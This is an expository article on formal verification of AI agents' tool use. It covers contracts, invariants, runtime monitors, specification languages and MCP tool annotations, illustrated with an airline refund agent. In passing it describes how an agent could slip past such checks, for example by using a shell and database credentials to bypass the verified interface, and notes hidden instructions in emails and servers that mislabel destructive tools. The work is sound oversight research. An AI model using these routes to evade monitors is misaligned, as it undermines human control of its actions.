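# Formal verification of AI agents' tool use, and whether proofs about effects scale to real software

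## What a proof about an agent's tool calls can say

Formal verification uses mathematical proof to show that a program meets a precise statement of what it may or must do. Engineers have long applied it to compilers and operating-system kernels. Researchers now also apply it to AI agents, programs in which a large language model chooses which tools to call and with what arguments. A tool can be almost any piece of software, such as a database query, a payment service, an email account or a command line. An agent's mistakes can be more serious than a chatbot's wrong sentence because its tool calls can delete files or send payments to the wrong person.

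### From a model's output to a changed database

A language model by itself only produces text. Anthropic's developer guide *How tool use works* describes how that text leads to actions. The developer supplies a list of tools, with the arguments each one accepts. When a task needs a tool, the model outputs a tool call, which gives the tool's name and arguments in a fixed format. The developer's program reads the call, runs the corresponding code and sends the result back to the model, which then outputs another call or a final answer. OpenAI's *Function calling* describes the same process. For a few tools, such as web search, Anthropic runs the code on its own servers. In both cases, a call has no effect until ordinary software acts on it, and that software can block the call.

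An effect is anything a call does besides returning a value, such as cancelling a booking in a database, sending a message or writing a file. Looking up a customer's record only returns a value, so it has no effect in this sense. Programmers call code with effects effectful. Its result depends on the state around it, and running it changes that state, so running it twice can do harm, such as sending a payment twice. The trace of a run is the ordered record of its tool calls, with their arguments and results.

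He, Desai and colleagues (2026), in *Soteria*, test a system for checking agents' plans on an airline's customer-service desk. A simplified desk makes a good running example. Its agent has four tools:

- get_reservation(r) returns the details of reservation r.
- check_flown(r) reports whether the passenger has already flown any part of it.
- cancel_reservation(r) marks it as cancelled.
- refund(r, a) pays back the amount a and records the refund.

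The tools use a database with two tables, one listing reservations and the amount paid for each, and the other listing refunds. The airline has a rule, invented here for illustration, that refunds for a reservation never total more than the customer paid. If a customer paid $300 and has already been refunded $200, the rule allows a further refund of $100 but not one of $150.

An agent could break this rule in ordinary ways. A customer might complain twice in separate conversations, or paste in a message with instructions that mislead the model. Trying the agent out gives some idea of how often such things happen. In one evaluation, Claude Opus 4.6, an Anthropic model that newer ones have since replaced, handled 50 airline tasks with the airline's policy in plain English and nothing to enforce it. It broke none of the rules in 82% of the tasks. That rate describes only those 50 tasks, and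 the next customer may bring a case unlike any of them. In *Guardians of the Agents* (2025), Erik Meijer applies to such evaluations what programmers have long accepted about tests, which is that they can reveal bad behaviour but cannot establish that there is none. A proof covers every case, including those nobody thought of trying, but somebody has to write down exactly what the cases are and what it means to keep the rule.

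### Writing the rule down

A specification is a precise formal statement of what a program may or must do. For the refund rule, let paid(r) be the amount the customer paid for reservation r, and let refunded(r) be the sum of all the rows for r in the refunds table. The specification is then:

> for every reservation r, refunded(r) ≤ paid(r)

A statement about the state that must hold at every step, like this one, is an invariant. Proving it requires an equally precise account of what each tool does. The standard notation goes back to Hoare's *An Axiomatic Basis for Computer Programming* (1969). A Hoare triple, which people now write {P} c {Q}, consists of a precondition P, a piece of code c and a postcondition Q. For the refund tool one can write:

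> {refunded(r) = t and a > 0 and t + a ≤ paid(r)} refund(r, a) {refunded(r) = t + a}

This means that if the refunds for reservation r so far total t, a is a positive amount, and t plus a is no more than the customer paid, then running refund(r, a) to completion will bring the refunds for r to t plus a. Hoare's triples describe only programs that terminate successfully, so a refund call that crashes halfway satisfies the triple whatever it has done to the database by then. A tool's precondition and postcondition together make up its contract.

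Under this contract, a buggy refund tool could add the right row and also reset paid(r) to zero or add a second row for somebody else's reservation, and the triple would still be true. A frame condition rules out these errors by specifying what a call must leave unchanged, which here is every amount in the reservations table and all refunds for reservations other than r. Meijer shows the same problem with files. A user asks for the deletion of foo.txt and bar.txt, and the model writes a plan that deletes every text file in the folder. The plan satisfies a specification that requires only that those two files be gone at the end, but not one that also requires all other files to remain.

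Given the frame conditions, the refund rule follows by induction on the length of the trace. At the start the refunds table is empty, so the rule holds. get_reservation and check_flown change nothing. Cancelling changes a reservation's status but, by its frame condition, no payment or refund. A refund raises refunded(r) from t to t + a, and the precondition guarantees that t + a is at most paid(r). Every call therefore preserves the rule, and the rule holds after any number of calls in any order, provided that something stops refund from running when its precondition is false.

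Lamport (2024), in *A Retrospective of Proving the Correctness of Multiprocess Programs*, calls such invariants inductive, meaning that any step from a state that satisfies the invariant leads to another state that satisfies it, even if the program could never reach the first state. A true invariant need not be inductive. Suppose the refund tool checked a running total stored with the reservation instead of adding up the refund rows. A state with an out-of-date total could satisfy the refund rule and still let a bad refund through on the next call. Whoever writes the proof would have to add a clause saying that the stored total always equals the sum of the rows, and prove it together with the refund rule.

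### Safety and liveness

The refund rule forbids something. An airline will also have rules that demand something, for instance that a customer who is owed a refund eventually gets it. Lamport's *Proving the Correctness of Multiprocess Programs* (1977) named the two kinds safety properties and liveness properties: nothing bad happens, and something required eventually happens. Alpern and Schneider (1985), in *Defining Liveness*, gave liveness an exact definition and set it beside one for safety. They treat an execution as an infinite sequence of states (a run that stops repeats its last state for ever) and a property P as a set of executions. Let σ be an execution, σ[i] its first i states, α any finite beginning and β any infinite continuation. Then:

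P is a safety property if every sequence σ outside P has a finite prefix σ[i] such that σ[i]β is outside P for every continuation β. P is a liveness property if every finite sequence α has a continuation β such that αβ is in P.

A safety violation happens at an identifiable moment, and nothing afterwards can repair it. Once the refunds on a $300 payment total $350, the airline has broken its rule, even if it recovers the money later. A liveness property can always still be satisfied, since the refund may come tomorrow. Alpern and Schneider also proved that every property is the intersection of a safety property and a liveness property.

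Some safety rules concern the order of calls, not just the current state. For example, the airline may forbid the agent from canceling a reservation until check_flown has reported that no part of it has been flown. We can express this rule as an invariant by adding a variable that records which reservations have passed the check. Lamport points out that any safety property can be turned into an invariant by adding variables.

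This distinction determines what a mechanism can enforce. A component that inspects calls one at a time can uphold a safety property by blocking the call that would break it, but blocking doesn't help when the violation is a missing call. He and colleagues encountered this problem with a rule that an agent must read a file back after writing it. A filter on individual calls could block a write that lacked an earlier read, but it could not make the later read happen. Their system checks in advance that every successful path through the plan includes the read.

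Safety properties alone are also easy to satisfy. According to the newsletter Computer Things, a system that does nothing satisfies all of them. An airline agent that refuses every refund will never exceed the refund limit, but it won't be useful to customers. A deadline makes liveness easier to handle. "A refund within seven days" is a safety property because it can fail at a definite moment.

### Who checks the proof

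Two kinds of software do most of the checking. One is an automated verifier such as Dafny. The programmer writes the code and its contracts, and the verifier translates both into logical formulas for a solver to check. For example, if a customer paid p and has already been refunded t, a further refund of a must keep t + a ≤ p. If the code checks this before paying, the solver has to prove that t + a ≤ p follows from t ≤ p, a > 0 and t + a ≤ p, which is trivial. Without the check, the last assumption disappears, the conclusion no longer follows, and the solver can produce a counterexample such as t = 200, a = 150 and p = 300. Real programs produce much harder formulas, and He and colleagues list as a limitation that the solver may not settle them all.

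With a proof assistant, such as Lean or Rocq, someone has to write the proof, and a small program called the kernel checks every step. Meijer (2026), in *I've never seen anything scarier than an LLM with tool calls*, contrasts the two approaches and adds that language models can now write the proofs. The kernel rejects a faulty proof whoever wrote it, so a safety proof can be accepted even from the same kind of model whose actions are in doubt.

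Every proof depends on a trusted computing base, which is everything that must be correct for the guarantee to hold but that nobody has proved. It normally includes the proof assistant's kernel or the solver, the compiler, the operating system and the hardware. Hoare already made results conditional on the compiler and the machine in 1969. The trusted base also includes the specification, since a proof of the wrong rule is still a valid proof. For agents, it often includes the tool contracts too. If the real refund tool converts the amount into another currency after checking it, every proof that relies on the contract stays valid while customers receive too much money. Trusted parts do fail in practice, and the Linux kernel contained the Copy Fail flaw for nearly a decade.

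### Four places to attach a proof

Some check has to stop a refund call whose precondition is false. *Toward Safe LLM Agents* (Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues, 2026), a survey of 38 studies, sorts the possible checks by whether they happen before, during or after execution. For building a guarantee, it is more useful to sort them by which of four places they are made in, because the place determines what needs proving and how often.

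The model can write a whole plan or program before any tool runs. For example, OpenAI's *Programmatic Tool Calling* lets a model write JavaScript that calls tools inside loops and conditions. A checker can look for any path through such a program that might issue a refund without comparing it to the amount paid, and Meijer proposes that agents submit a proof with each plan. The result covers every run of that plan, but each new plan needs its own proof.

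If the model must write in a restricted language, the language's designer can prove something once about every program that could be written in it. For example, if the language has no way to refer to the refund tool, no program written in it can issue a refund. OpenAI's runtime has a similar restriction, though without a proof. The generated JavaScript has no direct network access and can reach outside systems only through the tools that the developer has enabled.

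A runtime monitor checks each proposed tool call against the specification and blocks violations. For the airline, it would add up the earlier refunds and allow the new one only if the total stayed within the limit. The proof must show that the monitor's own code never allows a call that violates the specification. *Containment Verification* (Moon and Varshney, 2026) gives such a proof in Dafny for a model of PocketFlow, a very small framework for building agents. It proves that the modeled framework's central loop permits file reads only inside a chosen folder, calls only to approved tools, and no more than a set number of steps.

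Finally, a proof can cover the code of the tools. If the refund function provably rejects any amount over the limit, it does so for every caller, including the airline's own staff and other programs. But whoever builds the agent may not control that code, and it may enforce very little. In the airline example of He and colleagues, the cancellation tool carries out any cancellation it receives, eligible or not.

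A proof about a plan usually assumes that the tools meet their contracts, and a proof of the tools' code can show that they do. Hoare saw the same use for proofs of subroutines, since a subroutine's correctness, once proved, can serve as a lemma in the proof of every program that calls it.

### Why the model itself needs no proof

Nobody knows how to prove that a large language model will choose well on every input, and none of these approaches requires it. In Moon and Varshney's Dafny code, the model appears as a procedure with no body. The verifier can assume only that the procedure returns an action from a fixed set of types, so it must prove that the policy holds for every such action. Specialists call this havoc. The induction for the refund rule likewise checked each tool in turn, without considering why the agent had called it. A model that misreads the policy, obeys an instruction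 hidden in an email or tries to steal money produces a different sequence of calls, but the proof covers all sequences. A plan checker also examines only the plan, so its result doesn't depend on how the model produced it.

This independence limits the proof to calls and state, so an agent that refunds $100 to a customer who was owed nothing still follows the rule, as does one that lies to the customer about the refund. The argument also depends on what Moon and Varshney call effect exclusivity, the assumption that every effect the agent can have passes through the interface the proof describes. If the airline agent has a general-purpose command line and the database password, it can write to the refunds table directly. The theorem about the refund tool would still be true, but it would no longer protect the airline's money.

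## Stating which effects are allowed

The refund limit is one rule, but a real policy contains dozens, mixed with definitions and advice on tone. Somebody has to decide which sentences a checker can enforce and write a formula for each. For the airline benchmark, He and colleagues needed 24 formulas, which they wrote in a few hours. Mistakes in this step carry through to every later proof, including the Lean proof that *LeanGuard* (2026) gives for its procedure for admitting tool calls.

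### Six kinds of rule

The airline's desk needs several kinds of rules. In the formulas below, c.r is argument r of call c, and c.result is the value the call returned. The ordering and origin rules adapt examples from He and colleagues, and the others are illustrations.

| Kind of rule | In English | Formula |
|---|---|---|
| Limit on arguments | No single refund exceeds $1,000 | for every refund call c: 0 < c.a ≤ 1000 |
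| Ordering | The agent checks that nobody has flown before it cancels | for every cancel_reservation call c there is an earlier check_flown call d with d.r = c.r and d.result = false |
| Origin of a value | The refund amount comes from the airline's records | for every refund call c there is an earlier get_reservation call d with d.r = c.r, and c.a derives from d.result |
| State invariant | Refunds never total more than the customer paid | in every state, for every reservation r: refunded(r) ≤ paid(r) |
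| Frame condition | Cancelling changes one reservation's status and nothing else | for every cancel_reservation call c and reservation q: paid(q) and refunded(q) are the same after c as before, and so is status(q) unless q = c.r |
| Required follow-up | Every cancellation leads to a refund | for every cancel_reservation call c there is a later refund call d with d.r = c.r |

Omitting one condition from these formulas can allow effects they were meant to forbid. If the ordering rule lacked d.r = c.r, a check on any reservation would permit the agent to cancel all the others. If it lacked d.result = false, the agent could run the check, learn that the passenger had already flown, and cancel anyway. Even the full formula accepts a check from two hours ago, although the passenger may have boarded since.

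The origin rule guards against a model making up a plausible amount. To check such rules, He and colleagues tag each variable in a plan with the tools whose results contributed to its value. A variable computed from two others gets the tags of both, and a variable set to a constant gets none. But the tags don't distinguish between calls to get_reservation. Suppose an agent looks up a $300 reservation and a $900 one, then refunds $900 on the $300 one. The plan satisfies the rule in this form, because the agent looked up the reservation it refunded and the amount came from a lookup, but the refund limit catches the error.

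That limit has to refer to the database because the airline's staff also issue refunds, which don't appear in the agent's trace. Ordinary policies also contain frame conditions, usually without using the term. For example, the benchmark's airline lets the agent update the passengers on a booking but not change their number, which He and colleagues write as |new_pax| = |old_pax|.

### What each language can express

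He and colleagues write their rules as first-order formulas over traces. These formulas can refer to every call of a certain kind, or to at least one, and can compare any argument or result with any other. This makes it easy to require that a check and a cancellation concern the same reservation, even if nobody knew the reservation number in advance. A program can test a recorded trace against such a formula by looping over the calls. Reasoning about all possible traces is harder, because no algorithm can decide in general whether two first-order formulas mean the same thing. Plain first-order logic also cannot add up an arbitrary number of refunds, so the refund limit needs an added sum function.

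Temporal logic builds formulas from yes-or-no statements about each step, joined by operators such as "always", "eventually" and "until". It is the most common formal basis in the survey by Dantas and colleagues, where 13 of 38 studies use it. For a single reservation, the follow-up rule becomes "always (cancelled implies eventually refunded)". The classical version describes infinite runs. In LTLf, the version for finite traces, "eventually" means "before the trace ends", which suits agents if somebody defines when a conversation has ended. Software can convert any LTLf formula into a finite automaton, a machine with a fixed number of states that reads a trace step by step and accepts or rejects it. Comparing the automata for two formulas shows whether they allow the same traces. Because the set of statements is fixed, expressing "cancelled the same reservation that it checked" takes a separate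 copy of the formula for each reservation.

Access-control languages answer a narrower question, which is whether to permit one request now. Mondl, Maisel and Brock (2026), in *Autoformalization of Agent Instructions into Policy-as-Code*, use Cedar, an open-source language from Amazon Web Services. In Cedar the refund limit could look like this:

`forbid (principal, action == Action::"refund", resource) when { context.refunded + context.amount > context.paid };`

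An engineer with no training in logic can read that line. But Cedar doesn't keep a record of earlier refunds, so the surrounding program must look them up and pass in the total. If that total is out of date, the policy can permit a refund that it should block. Mondl and colleagues list rules about the order of actions as a gap they have not yet closed.

| Kind of rule | First-order formulas over traces | Temporal logic on finite traces | Cedar |
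|---|---|---|---|
| Limit on arguments | Yes | Yes, given a statement such as "amount over $1,000" | Yes |
| Ordering | Yes | Yes, for reservations known in advance | Only if the host program supplies the history |
| Origin of a value | Yes, if the trace records origins | Only if the host program labels values | Only if the host program labels values |
| State invariant | Yes, with access to the state and a sum function | Yes, given a statement such as "all totals within limits" | One call at a time, with totals from the host program |
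| Frame condition | Yes, if the trace records the state before and after | Yes, given a statement such as "nothing else changed" | No, since Cedar decides before the tool runs |
| Required follow-up | Yes | Yes, for reservations known in advance | No |

### Finding the rules

A policy document may omit the rule that matters most. *Towards Verifiably Safe Tool Use for LLM Agents* (Doshi, Hong and colleagues, 2026) describes a calendar agent that can list events, change them and send email. A user adds an appointment to treat a sexually transmitted disease, and the appointment clashes with a meeting with Bob. With no attacker involved and every tool working as intended, the agent moves the meeting and emails Bob, giving the reason in the subject line.

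To anticipate such cases, Doshi and colleagues adapt System-Theoretic Process Analysis (STPA), a method that safety engineers use in aviation and for self-driving cars. STPA looks for hazards that can arise from how parts interact, even when each part works correctly by itself. The analyst first lists everyone the agent affects, here the user and the other people at the meeting. The analyst then identifies what each of them values, such as privacy or prompt notice, and the loss that would result if the agent failed to respect it. The next steps are to work out which behaviour could cause each loss, decide which losses are serious enough to prevent, and write requirements against them. For example, the calendar agent must leave private information out of emails unless the user authorises it, and must promptly tell everyone at the meeting about a change.

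No program can check "private" or "promptly", so the requirements still have to be turned into specifications. The privacy requirement becomes an information-flow rule: only attendees may see event details, anything derived from private data is at least as private, and no email may contain data its recipient isn't allowed to see. The notice requirement becomes a temporal rule that an email to every attendee must directly follow each change. If "directly" is read strictly, this rule is impossible to satisfy with two attendees, because only one call can come immediately after the change.

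Doshi and colleagues then decide which of the agent's possible actions to block, require, allow freely or allow only with the user's confirmation. One cautious option they mention is to block all email once the agent has listed the calendar's events, but the agent could then never send the notices that the other rule requires. They have tried the method only on this small example, so it isn't known how many hazards it would find in a larger system. They also restrict it to agents with one narrow task, because they think nobody can state precise safety requirements for an agent that might do anything.

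### Translating prose into formulas

Language models can write formulas faster than people can by hand. The question is how often a formula means the same thing as the sentence it translates.

Dantas and colleagues conclude that this is the field's bottleneck. Their review took ten days in May 2026 and followed PRISMA 2020, a standard procedure for systematic reviews. They searched six databases, and one person screened 71 records, which left 38 studies. In September, three of them repeated the search and screened the results independently. Their decisions largely agreed (a kappa of 0.81, where 1 is perfect agreement), but the new search returned only 13 of the 38 studies and found ten eligible papers that the original search had missed, so the 38 are a sample of the field.

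Their main evidence on translation comes from Planetarium, a benchmark on which models translate descriptions into PDDL, a language for stating planning problems. GPT-4o, an OpenAI model from 2024, wrote valid PDDL 96.1% of the time, but only 24.8% of its translations described the right problem. The best fine-tuned model reached 34.2%. These models are old, and a PDDL problem states a starting situation and a goal, not a policy, so the figures don't predict how often a current model would get a refund rule wrong. But about three quarters of GPT-4o's valid translations were wrong, so a syntax check is almost useless as evidence that a translation is correct.

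The review grades its own evidence for nine principal claims on GRADE, a scale from medical research. Seven of the claims, including the Planetarium figures, get the lowest rating, Very Low, and the other two get Moderate. Even these ratings are generous, because the review starts every claim at High, whereas the GRADE guidelines start observational studies at Low.

It concludes overall that no existing approach combines soundness (never passing an unsafe plan), completeness (never rejecting a safe one), scalability, semantic grounding (formulas that match what people meant) and utility preservation (an agent that still gets its work done). Part of this limit is permanent, because Rice's theorem (1953) rules out any checker for unrestricted programs that is sound, complete and certain to finish. No such theorem rules out semantic grounding, and newer work has made some progress on it.

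*A Neurosymbolic Approach to Natural Language Formalization and Verification* (An, Bayless and colleagues) describes a commercial service from Amazon Web Services that checks a chatbot's answers against a company's written policy. A model turns each passage of the policy into variables and logical rules, and software merges the variables that appear to mean the same thing. When the chatbot answers a question, three models separately translate the answer into logic. The service approves an answer only if all three translations agree and a solver shows that the conclusion follows from the rules.

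The service made 1,689 decisions using policies that no human had corrected, and it wrongly approved 10 answers. An and colleagues report this as 99.4% soundness, meaning that 99.4% of all decisions were not wrong approvals. They recognise that a service that approved nothing would score 100%, so they also report that their service approved just 14.9% of the correct answers. It approved 179 answers in all, so about one approval in 18 was wrong. That is much better than the Planetarium figures suggest, although the tasks differ, but the error rate is too high for a specification that will govern payments without review.

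An and colleagues found that human review improved an automatic translation of the airline Ryanair's refund policy. After people spent several hours correcting the translation, wrong approvals on 62 test items fell from two to none, and the share of correct answers approved rose from 25% to 45.5%. Only about a third of the items were new to the people making the corrections, so the improvement on new questions may be smaller.

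Some of what they fixed was the policy itself. It offers a possible refund when a flight leaves at least five hours late, but it's unclear whether a passenger who flew anyway qualifies. A better translator can't settle that, and the airline has to decide. In another place, the policy denies a refund to anyone who missed a flight that operated, and a later section grants one to passengers whom the airline refused to board. People read the later passage as an exception. The model had translated the two as separate rules:

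> flight operated and passenger did not travel → not eligible
>
> boarding denied → eligible

If a passenger was turned away at the gate and the flight then left, the passenger counted as both eligible and ineligible, so the solver reported that this situation could not occur.

Translation into temporal logic has also improved. *NeuroSTAR* (2026) uses several models to propose LTLf formulas, compares the automata to find where the proposals differ, and uses the differences to steer the models towards one formula. It reached 96.4% and 100% accuracy on two strict datasets. Before the evaluation, its developers removed 48.43% of the benchmark data because they found ambiguities and inconsistencies, so the scores apply to sentences with one clear meaning. On driving law, the main obstacle was vocabulary, since a formula can only mention things for which someone has defined a statement. Quansah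 and Bonnah (2026), in *NeuroNL2LTL*, describe an older trade-off between templates, which are reliable but can express little, and neural translation, which is fluent but not guaranteed to be correct. Their system first translates English into an intermediate form, and the step from there to temporal logic preserves structure by construction. The first step still relies on a learned model.

All these accuracy figures depend on reference answers, which a company with a new policy doesn't have. *Faithful Autoformalization via Roundtrip Verification and Repair*, by Amrollahi, Lopez and Barrett, proposes a check that doesn't need them. A model formalises a sentence, translates the formula back into English, and formalises that translation. A solver then tests whether the two formulas are equivalent. A mismatch points to the step that went wrong. Agreement is weaker evidence that the formalisation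 is correct, because a model can misread a phrase such as "at least five hours late" the same way both times.

### When nobody has stated the rule

Many of the rules that software should follow are known only to the people who wrote it. Anthropic measured how much this matters in a December 2026 study of 21 known logic bugs, in which a program breaks a rule it should follow. According to Help Net Security's *Anthropic’s AI bug tests uncover previously undisclosed flaws*, the bugs came from the SQLite database and three libraries for images and compression. The researchers gave Claude Mythos 5 the source code from before each fix and let it submit up to 1,000 inputs in each of three runs. It got credit for a bug if any input produced different results in the fixed and unfixed versions.

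One method was an informal correctness proof, which argues that the code obeys an invariant but is not checked by a proof assistant. This method found 8 of the 21 bugs when the model had to infer the invariant from the code, and all 21 when the researchers supplied it. Code review by the model also improved when the invariant was supplied, from 11 bugs found to 20.

The comparison somewhat exaggerates the difference. The researchers knew which invariant each bug broke, so supplying it also gave the model a rough idea of where to look. An engineer with new code would have to write many invariants without knowing which ones fail. Later models could recall most of the bugs disclosed up to 2024, but this is a smaller concern because recall should have helped more when the model had no invariant. Models are also quickly getting better at inferring invariants. With none supplied, Claude Sonnet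 4.5 found one bug by code review, Claude Opus 4.5 found five and Claude Mythos 5.2 found 15. For now, though, a person who can state the invariant still helps a lot.

*Agentic Property-Based Testing* (Maaz, DeVoe and colleagues, 2025) describes an agent that inferred properties of Python libraries from their code and documentation, then searched for inputs that broke them. The agent's bug reports were valid 56% of the time. A tool's developer could use inferred properties as suggestions for a specification, but would have to review each one.

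### Testing a specification

A specification can contain bugs like any other program, and several kinds of test find them. The simplest is to go through the policy clause by clause and find the formula for each. He and colleagues do this for every rule that concerns a state change and can be checked from the trace of tool calls. This exposes missing formulas, but a formula can still be wrong. For example, their airline policy requires a changed flight to keep its origin and destination, but the formula they print accepts any new route if the cabin class also changes. They abbreviate their formulas in print, so the code may be stricter. They also say they later corrected misstated rules and added missing ones while auditing their results.

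Example traces catch such errors. For the refund limit, the earlier refunds of $100 and $150 give one trace to accept and one to reject. The best examples to reject come from real misbehaviour. In one test, an agent without safeguards upgraded a reservation to business class, which made it eligible for cancellation, and then cancelled it. He and colleagues count this as a violation, but their eligibility formula requires only an earlier lookup showing business class, or one of several other grounds. An agent that upgraded the reservation, looked it up again, ran the flown check and then cancelled would satisfy both of their cancellation formulas as printed. Adding that trace to a list of traces to reject would expose the gap.

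The traces a specification must accept matter just as much, as the results of Mondl and colleagues show. They started with an 88-rule policy for agents that handle medical records. Another group had drafted it with GPT-5.2, expanded it using STPA, and coded 23 of the rules by hand. Mondl and colleagues had a model translate the policy into Cedar and replayed recorded runs against the result. The Cedar policy blocked 167 of 300 ordinary runs in which the 23 hand-coded rules had detected nothing unsafe, which they attribute to wider coverage. But it also blocked 85 of the 86 runs that tried to write to a record. A policy that forbade all writing would score even higher, but no hospital could use it. Because they measured coverage and not usefulness, their results don't show whether the specification is thorough or overly strict.

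Doshi and colleagues use Alloy, a modelling tool that tries every trace up to a fixed size, to test whether their rules block unsafe traces and still allow safe ones. Without the rules, Alloy quickly found traces that leaked private data into an email. With the rules, it found no such leaks, and it could still find traces in which the agent moved a meeting and notified everyone safely. The result applies only to a model of the agent's tools and to traces within the size limit.

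Another way to test a specification is mutation testing, which means deliberately breaking a correct program and checking whether the specification rules out the result. He et al. give the example of a plan that looks up a reservation and cancels it if the booking is less than 24 hours old, but never checks whether the passenger has flown. Their verifier rejects the plan because of the ordering rule, and would accept it if that rule were missing. For the refund tool, the altered versions could include one that pays twice, along with the faulty ones that frame conditions should rule out. Each altered version that passes points to a missing rule, unless the change is harmless.

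Some rules are vacuously true, meaning that they never reject a trace. For example, a rule about every call to cancel_booking is true of all traces if the tool's name is cancel_reservation. The flight-change formula of He and colleagues has a mild form of this problem, because it applies to every earlier lookup of the reservation and so holds automatically if there was none. Another of their rules requires a lookup, so traces without one are still rejected. Mondl and colleagues use Cedar's analysis tools to flag vacuous and conflicting policies, and the Amazon service warns about unused variables and contradictory rules. A more thorough test uses a solver to search for a trace that breaks only the rule in question. If no such trace exists, the rule is redundant.

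Rules can also conflict only in a few situations, and a general search for contradictions will miss those conflicts. The follow-up rule and the refund limit from the airline's list conflict when a customer who paid $300 and has already received $300 back asks the agent to cancel the reservation. After the cancellation, the follow-up rule requires a refund of more than zero, and the limit forbids it. The pair looks consistent because most other reservations can satisfy both rules. A solver will find the problem if someone has it search for a state in which the agent may cancel but can't then meet its obligations. The airline can fix the rule by requiring a refund only when refunded(r) < paid(r).

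## Describing what each tool does

The refund limit constrains the state of a database, but an agent's plan contains only tool calls, so a proof needs a contract for each tool that describes how a call changes the state. A checker can't test the refund tool by running it, since that would pay out real money, and often can't read the tool's code because another company runs it. It has to assume that the tool meets its contract. A runtime monitor also depends on contracts, for instance that the lookup tool reports the true total of earlier refunds. Even a proof of the refund tool's own code depends on assumptions about the database and the payment service beneath it.

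### A contract for the refund tool

The Hoare triple for refund(r, a) covers only calls that succeed. Calls also fail, and agents retry them, so a usable contract must cover both failures and retries. Let t be the value of refunded(r) just before the call.

- Precondition: reservation r exists, a > 0, and t + a ≤ paid(r).
- Postcondition: when the tool reports success, refunded(r) = t + a, and the refunds table has exactly one new row.
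- Frame condition: paid(q) and status(q) stay the same for every reservation q, and refunded(q) stays the same for every q ≠ r. The tool contacts the payment service and no other outside system.
- Errors: if the tool reports that the bank declined the payment, nothing has changed. If no reply arrives, either nothing has changed or the postcondition holds.
- Repetition: not safe. A second identical call pays a again.

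The caller is responsible for making sure the precondition is true. When it is false, the contract guarantees nothing. For example, if the precondition is that the reservation has enough money left to cover the payout, a tool that pays out $150 on a reservation with only $100 left still meets the contract.

The lines on errors and repetition cover mistakes that the refund limit doesn't prevent. Suppose a customer who paid $300 is owed a $100 refund. The first call succeeds but its reply gets lost, so the agent calls again and the customer receives $200. The invariant holds because $200 is within the limit, but the airline has lost $100. Retries are safe only if the tool supports them, for example by accepting a key that marks both calls as the same refund.

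If one line of a tool's description is wrong, a valid proof may no longer guarantee that the real system follows the rule. Suppose the real refund tool pays at once but adds the row to the refunds table overnight, so the postcondition is false when the call returns. A customer who paid $300 gets $200 back in the morning and complains again in the afternoon. The monitor adds up the refunds in the table, finds none, and allows another $200. By the next day the table shows $400. The proof of the refund rule is still valid, but it relied on each call raising the total before the next one began.

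A contract can also contradict itself. If the frame condition omits q ≠ r, it requires refunded(r) to stay at t, while the postcondition requires it to be t + a. Both can't be true when a > 0, and because anything follows from a contradiction, an automated verifier could then accept any claim about the state after a successful refund, including that the airline has paid nobody. This error is fairly easy to look for by having the verifier try to prove 0 = 1 after each call. If it succeeds, something in the contract is wrong.

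### Where contracts come from

Many tools reach agents through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard. A provider runs a server, and the agent's software, the client, requests a list of tools from it. According to Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), each entry in the list has a name and an input schema, and can also include a prose description, an output schema and annotations about the tool's behaviour. Information about what a tool does can also come from its code, records of past calls and formal proofs.

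| Source | What it can supply for the refund tool | What it leaves open |
|---|---|---|
| Type schema | The amount is a number above zero | Everything about the database |
| Documentation | Limits, fees and errors, in prose | Whether the prose is complete and current |
| MCP annotations | The tool changes something, and repeating a call isn't safe | Which rows change, by how much and when |
| Analysis of the code | The kinds of effect the code can have | What happens inside databases and outside services |
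| Observed calls | What changed in the calls on record | Rare cases and anything nobody recorded |
| Proof of the implementation | Every line about the tool's own behaviour | The systems beneath the tool |

A schema can require a positive amount or cap it at $1,000, but it describes only the arguments, so it can't compare the amount with paid(r). Servers must return results that match a tool's output schema, if it has one, and clients should check them, but a reply with all the right fields can still contain a false total. Developers sometimes get even these simple declarations wrong. *Real Faults in Model Context Protocol (MCP) Software* (2026), a taxonomy of bugs, includes 16 issues in which a server declared or registered its tools incorrectly, such as with faulty names, schemas or parameter definitions.

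### The protocol's annotations

The Model Context Protocol (MCP) defines four true-or-false annotations that describe a tool's behaviour. The table below gives their definitions and defaults, and the last column applies them to the refund tool.

| Annotation | Meaning when true | Default | Refund tool |
|---|---|---|---|
| readOnlyHint | The tool does not modify its environment | False | False |
| destructiveHint | The tool may make destructive changes, not only additions | True | Debatable |
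| idempotentHint | Repeating a call with the same arguments has no further effect | False | False |
| openWorldHint | The tool may interact with outside entities | True | True, if it pays through a bank |

The refund tool only adds a row, so a developer could honestly set destructiveHint to false. But it also pays out the airline's money, and a client that skips its warning for "additive" tools would let the payment through.

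The defaults for a tool without annotations describe the worst case, which is sensible for a client deciding whether to ask the user but nearly useless for a proof. If get_reservation has no annotations, the verifier must allow that looking up a booking could have changed any row in the database, so it can no longer rely on anything it had established about earlier refunds.

Under the Model Context Protocol (MCP), "Clients should never make tool use decisions based on ToolAnnotations received from untrusted servers." Reviewers of the original proposal questioned what use annotations would then have, and Justin Spahr-Summers, one of MCP's creators, asked how a client could use a flag it couldn't trust. In the compromise, described in a blog post on the annotations (Model Context Protocol, 2026), every annotation is a hint, and each client decides how much weight to give it based on what it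 knows about the server. In practice, most clients trust a server because the user chose to install it. The post also warns that a server can declare a tool read-only and delete files anyway, and it advises developers to rely on deterministic controls for real guarantees. An airline that runs its own server can reasonably use the hints as assumptions in a proof, but someone who connects to a stranger's server can't.

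Trofimov and Novikov (2026), in *When Tool Calls Succeed but Workflows Fail*, measured how often developers use these hints. They asked every remote server in the official MCP registry for its tools in July 2026, and 4,838 servers returned 98,291 tools. Of these, 74% had at least one hint, but one publisher supplied 45% of all the tools and set all four hints on every one. Among the other publishers' tools, 47.2% had no hints. Trofimov and Novikov didn't call any of the tools, so their census doesn't show how often the hints are accurate.

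They also list what even accurate hints cannot express. A server can't use them to tell a client how to check whether an unconfirmed call took effect, how to undo a call, or which calls it can safely reorder. A tool can offer these things in its own way, but a client then has to learn how each tool does it.

### Richer declarations, and who reads them

*Small Agents Should Know What Their Tools Do* (Kovalenko and Redchych, 2026) tested a more detailed format on simulated office and shopping tools. Each tool declares whether it computes, reads, writes or makes a change that can't be undone. Refunds belong to the last group because they move money, which settles the question that destructiveHint leaves open. Each tool also declares whether repeating a call is safe and has a footprint, which lists the resources it reads and writes. For the airline's refund tool, the footprint might be "reads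 reservation r, writes the refunds of r". This gives a frame condition in one line, since everything outside the written resources must stay the same. The footprint doesn't include amounts, so it isn't enough to prove that refunds stay within the limit.

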